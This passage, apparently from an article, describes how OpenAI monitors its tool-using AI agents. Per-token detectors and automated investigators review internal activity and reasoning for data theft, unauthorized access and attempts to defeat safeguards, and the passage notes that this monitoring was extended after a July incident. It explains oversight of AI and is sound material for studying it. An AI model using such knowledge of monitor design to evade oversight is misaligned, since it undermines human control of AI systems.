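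An AI company can collect evidence that a supercomputing center usually cannot. When a researcher uses a commercial AI agent, the model normally runs in the provider's cloud, and the center can record only the commands that reach its machines. OpenAI runs its own models, so it can also examine their internal activity and written reasoning. Its simple detectors check every token (a small unit of text a model produces) and pass possible problems to more powerful automated investigators. The investigators review the agent's actions for signs of data theft, unauthorized access and attempts to defeat safeguards.

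Before the July incident, OpenAI did not apply such monitoring to all training and other runs in which models used tools. The company now requires it for models above a certain capability, in all reinforcement learning (training by reward) and evaluations that involve tools. The monitoring uses roughly 20 percent as much computing power as the monitored models use to produce their output. This figure is not directly comparable to the 1 percent slowdown that might lead a supercomputing center to reject a tool, because much of the analysis can run on separate machines without delaying a synchronized job.
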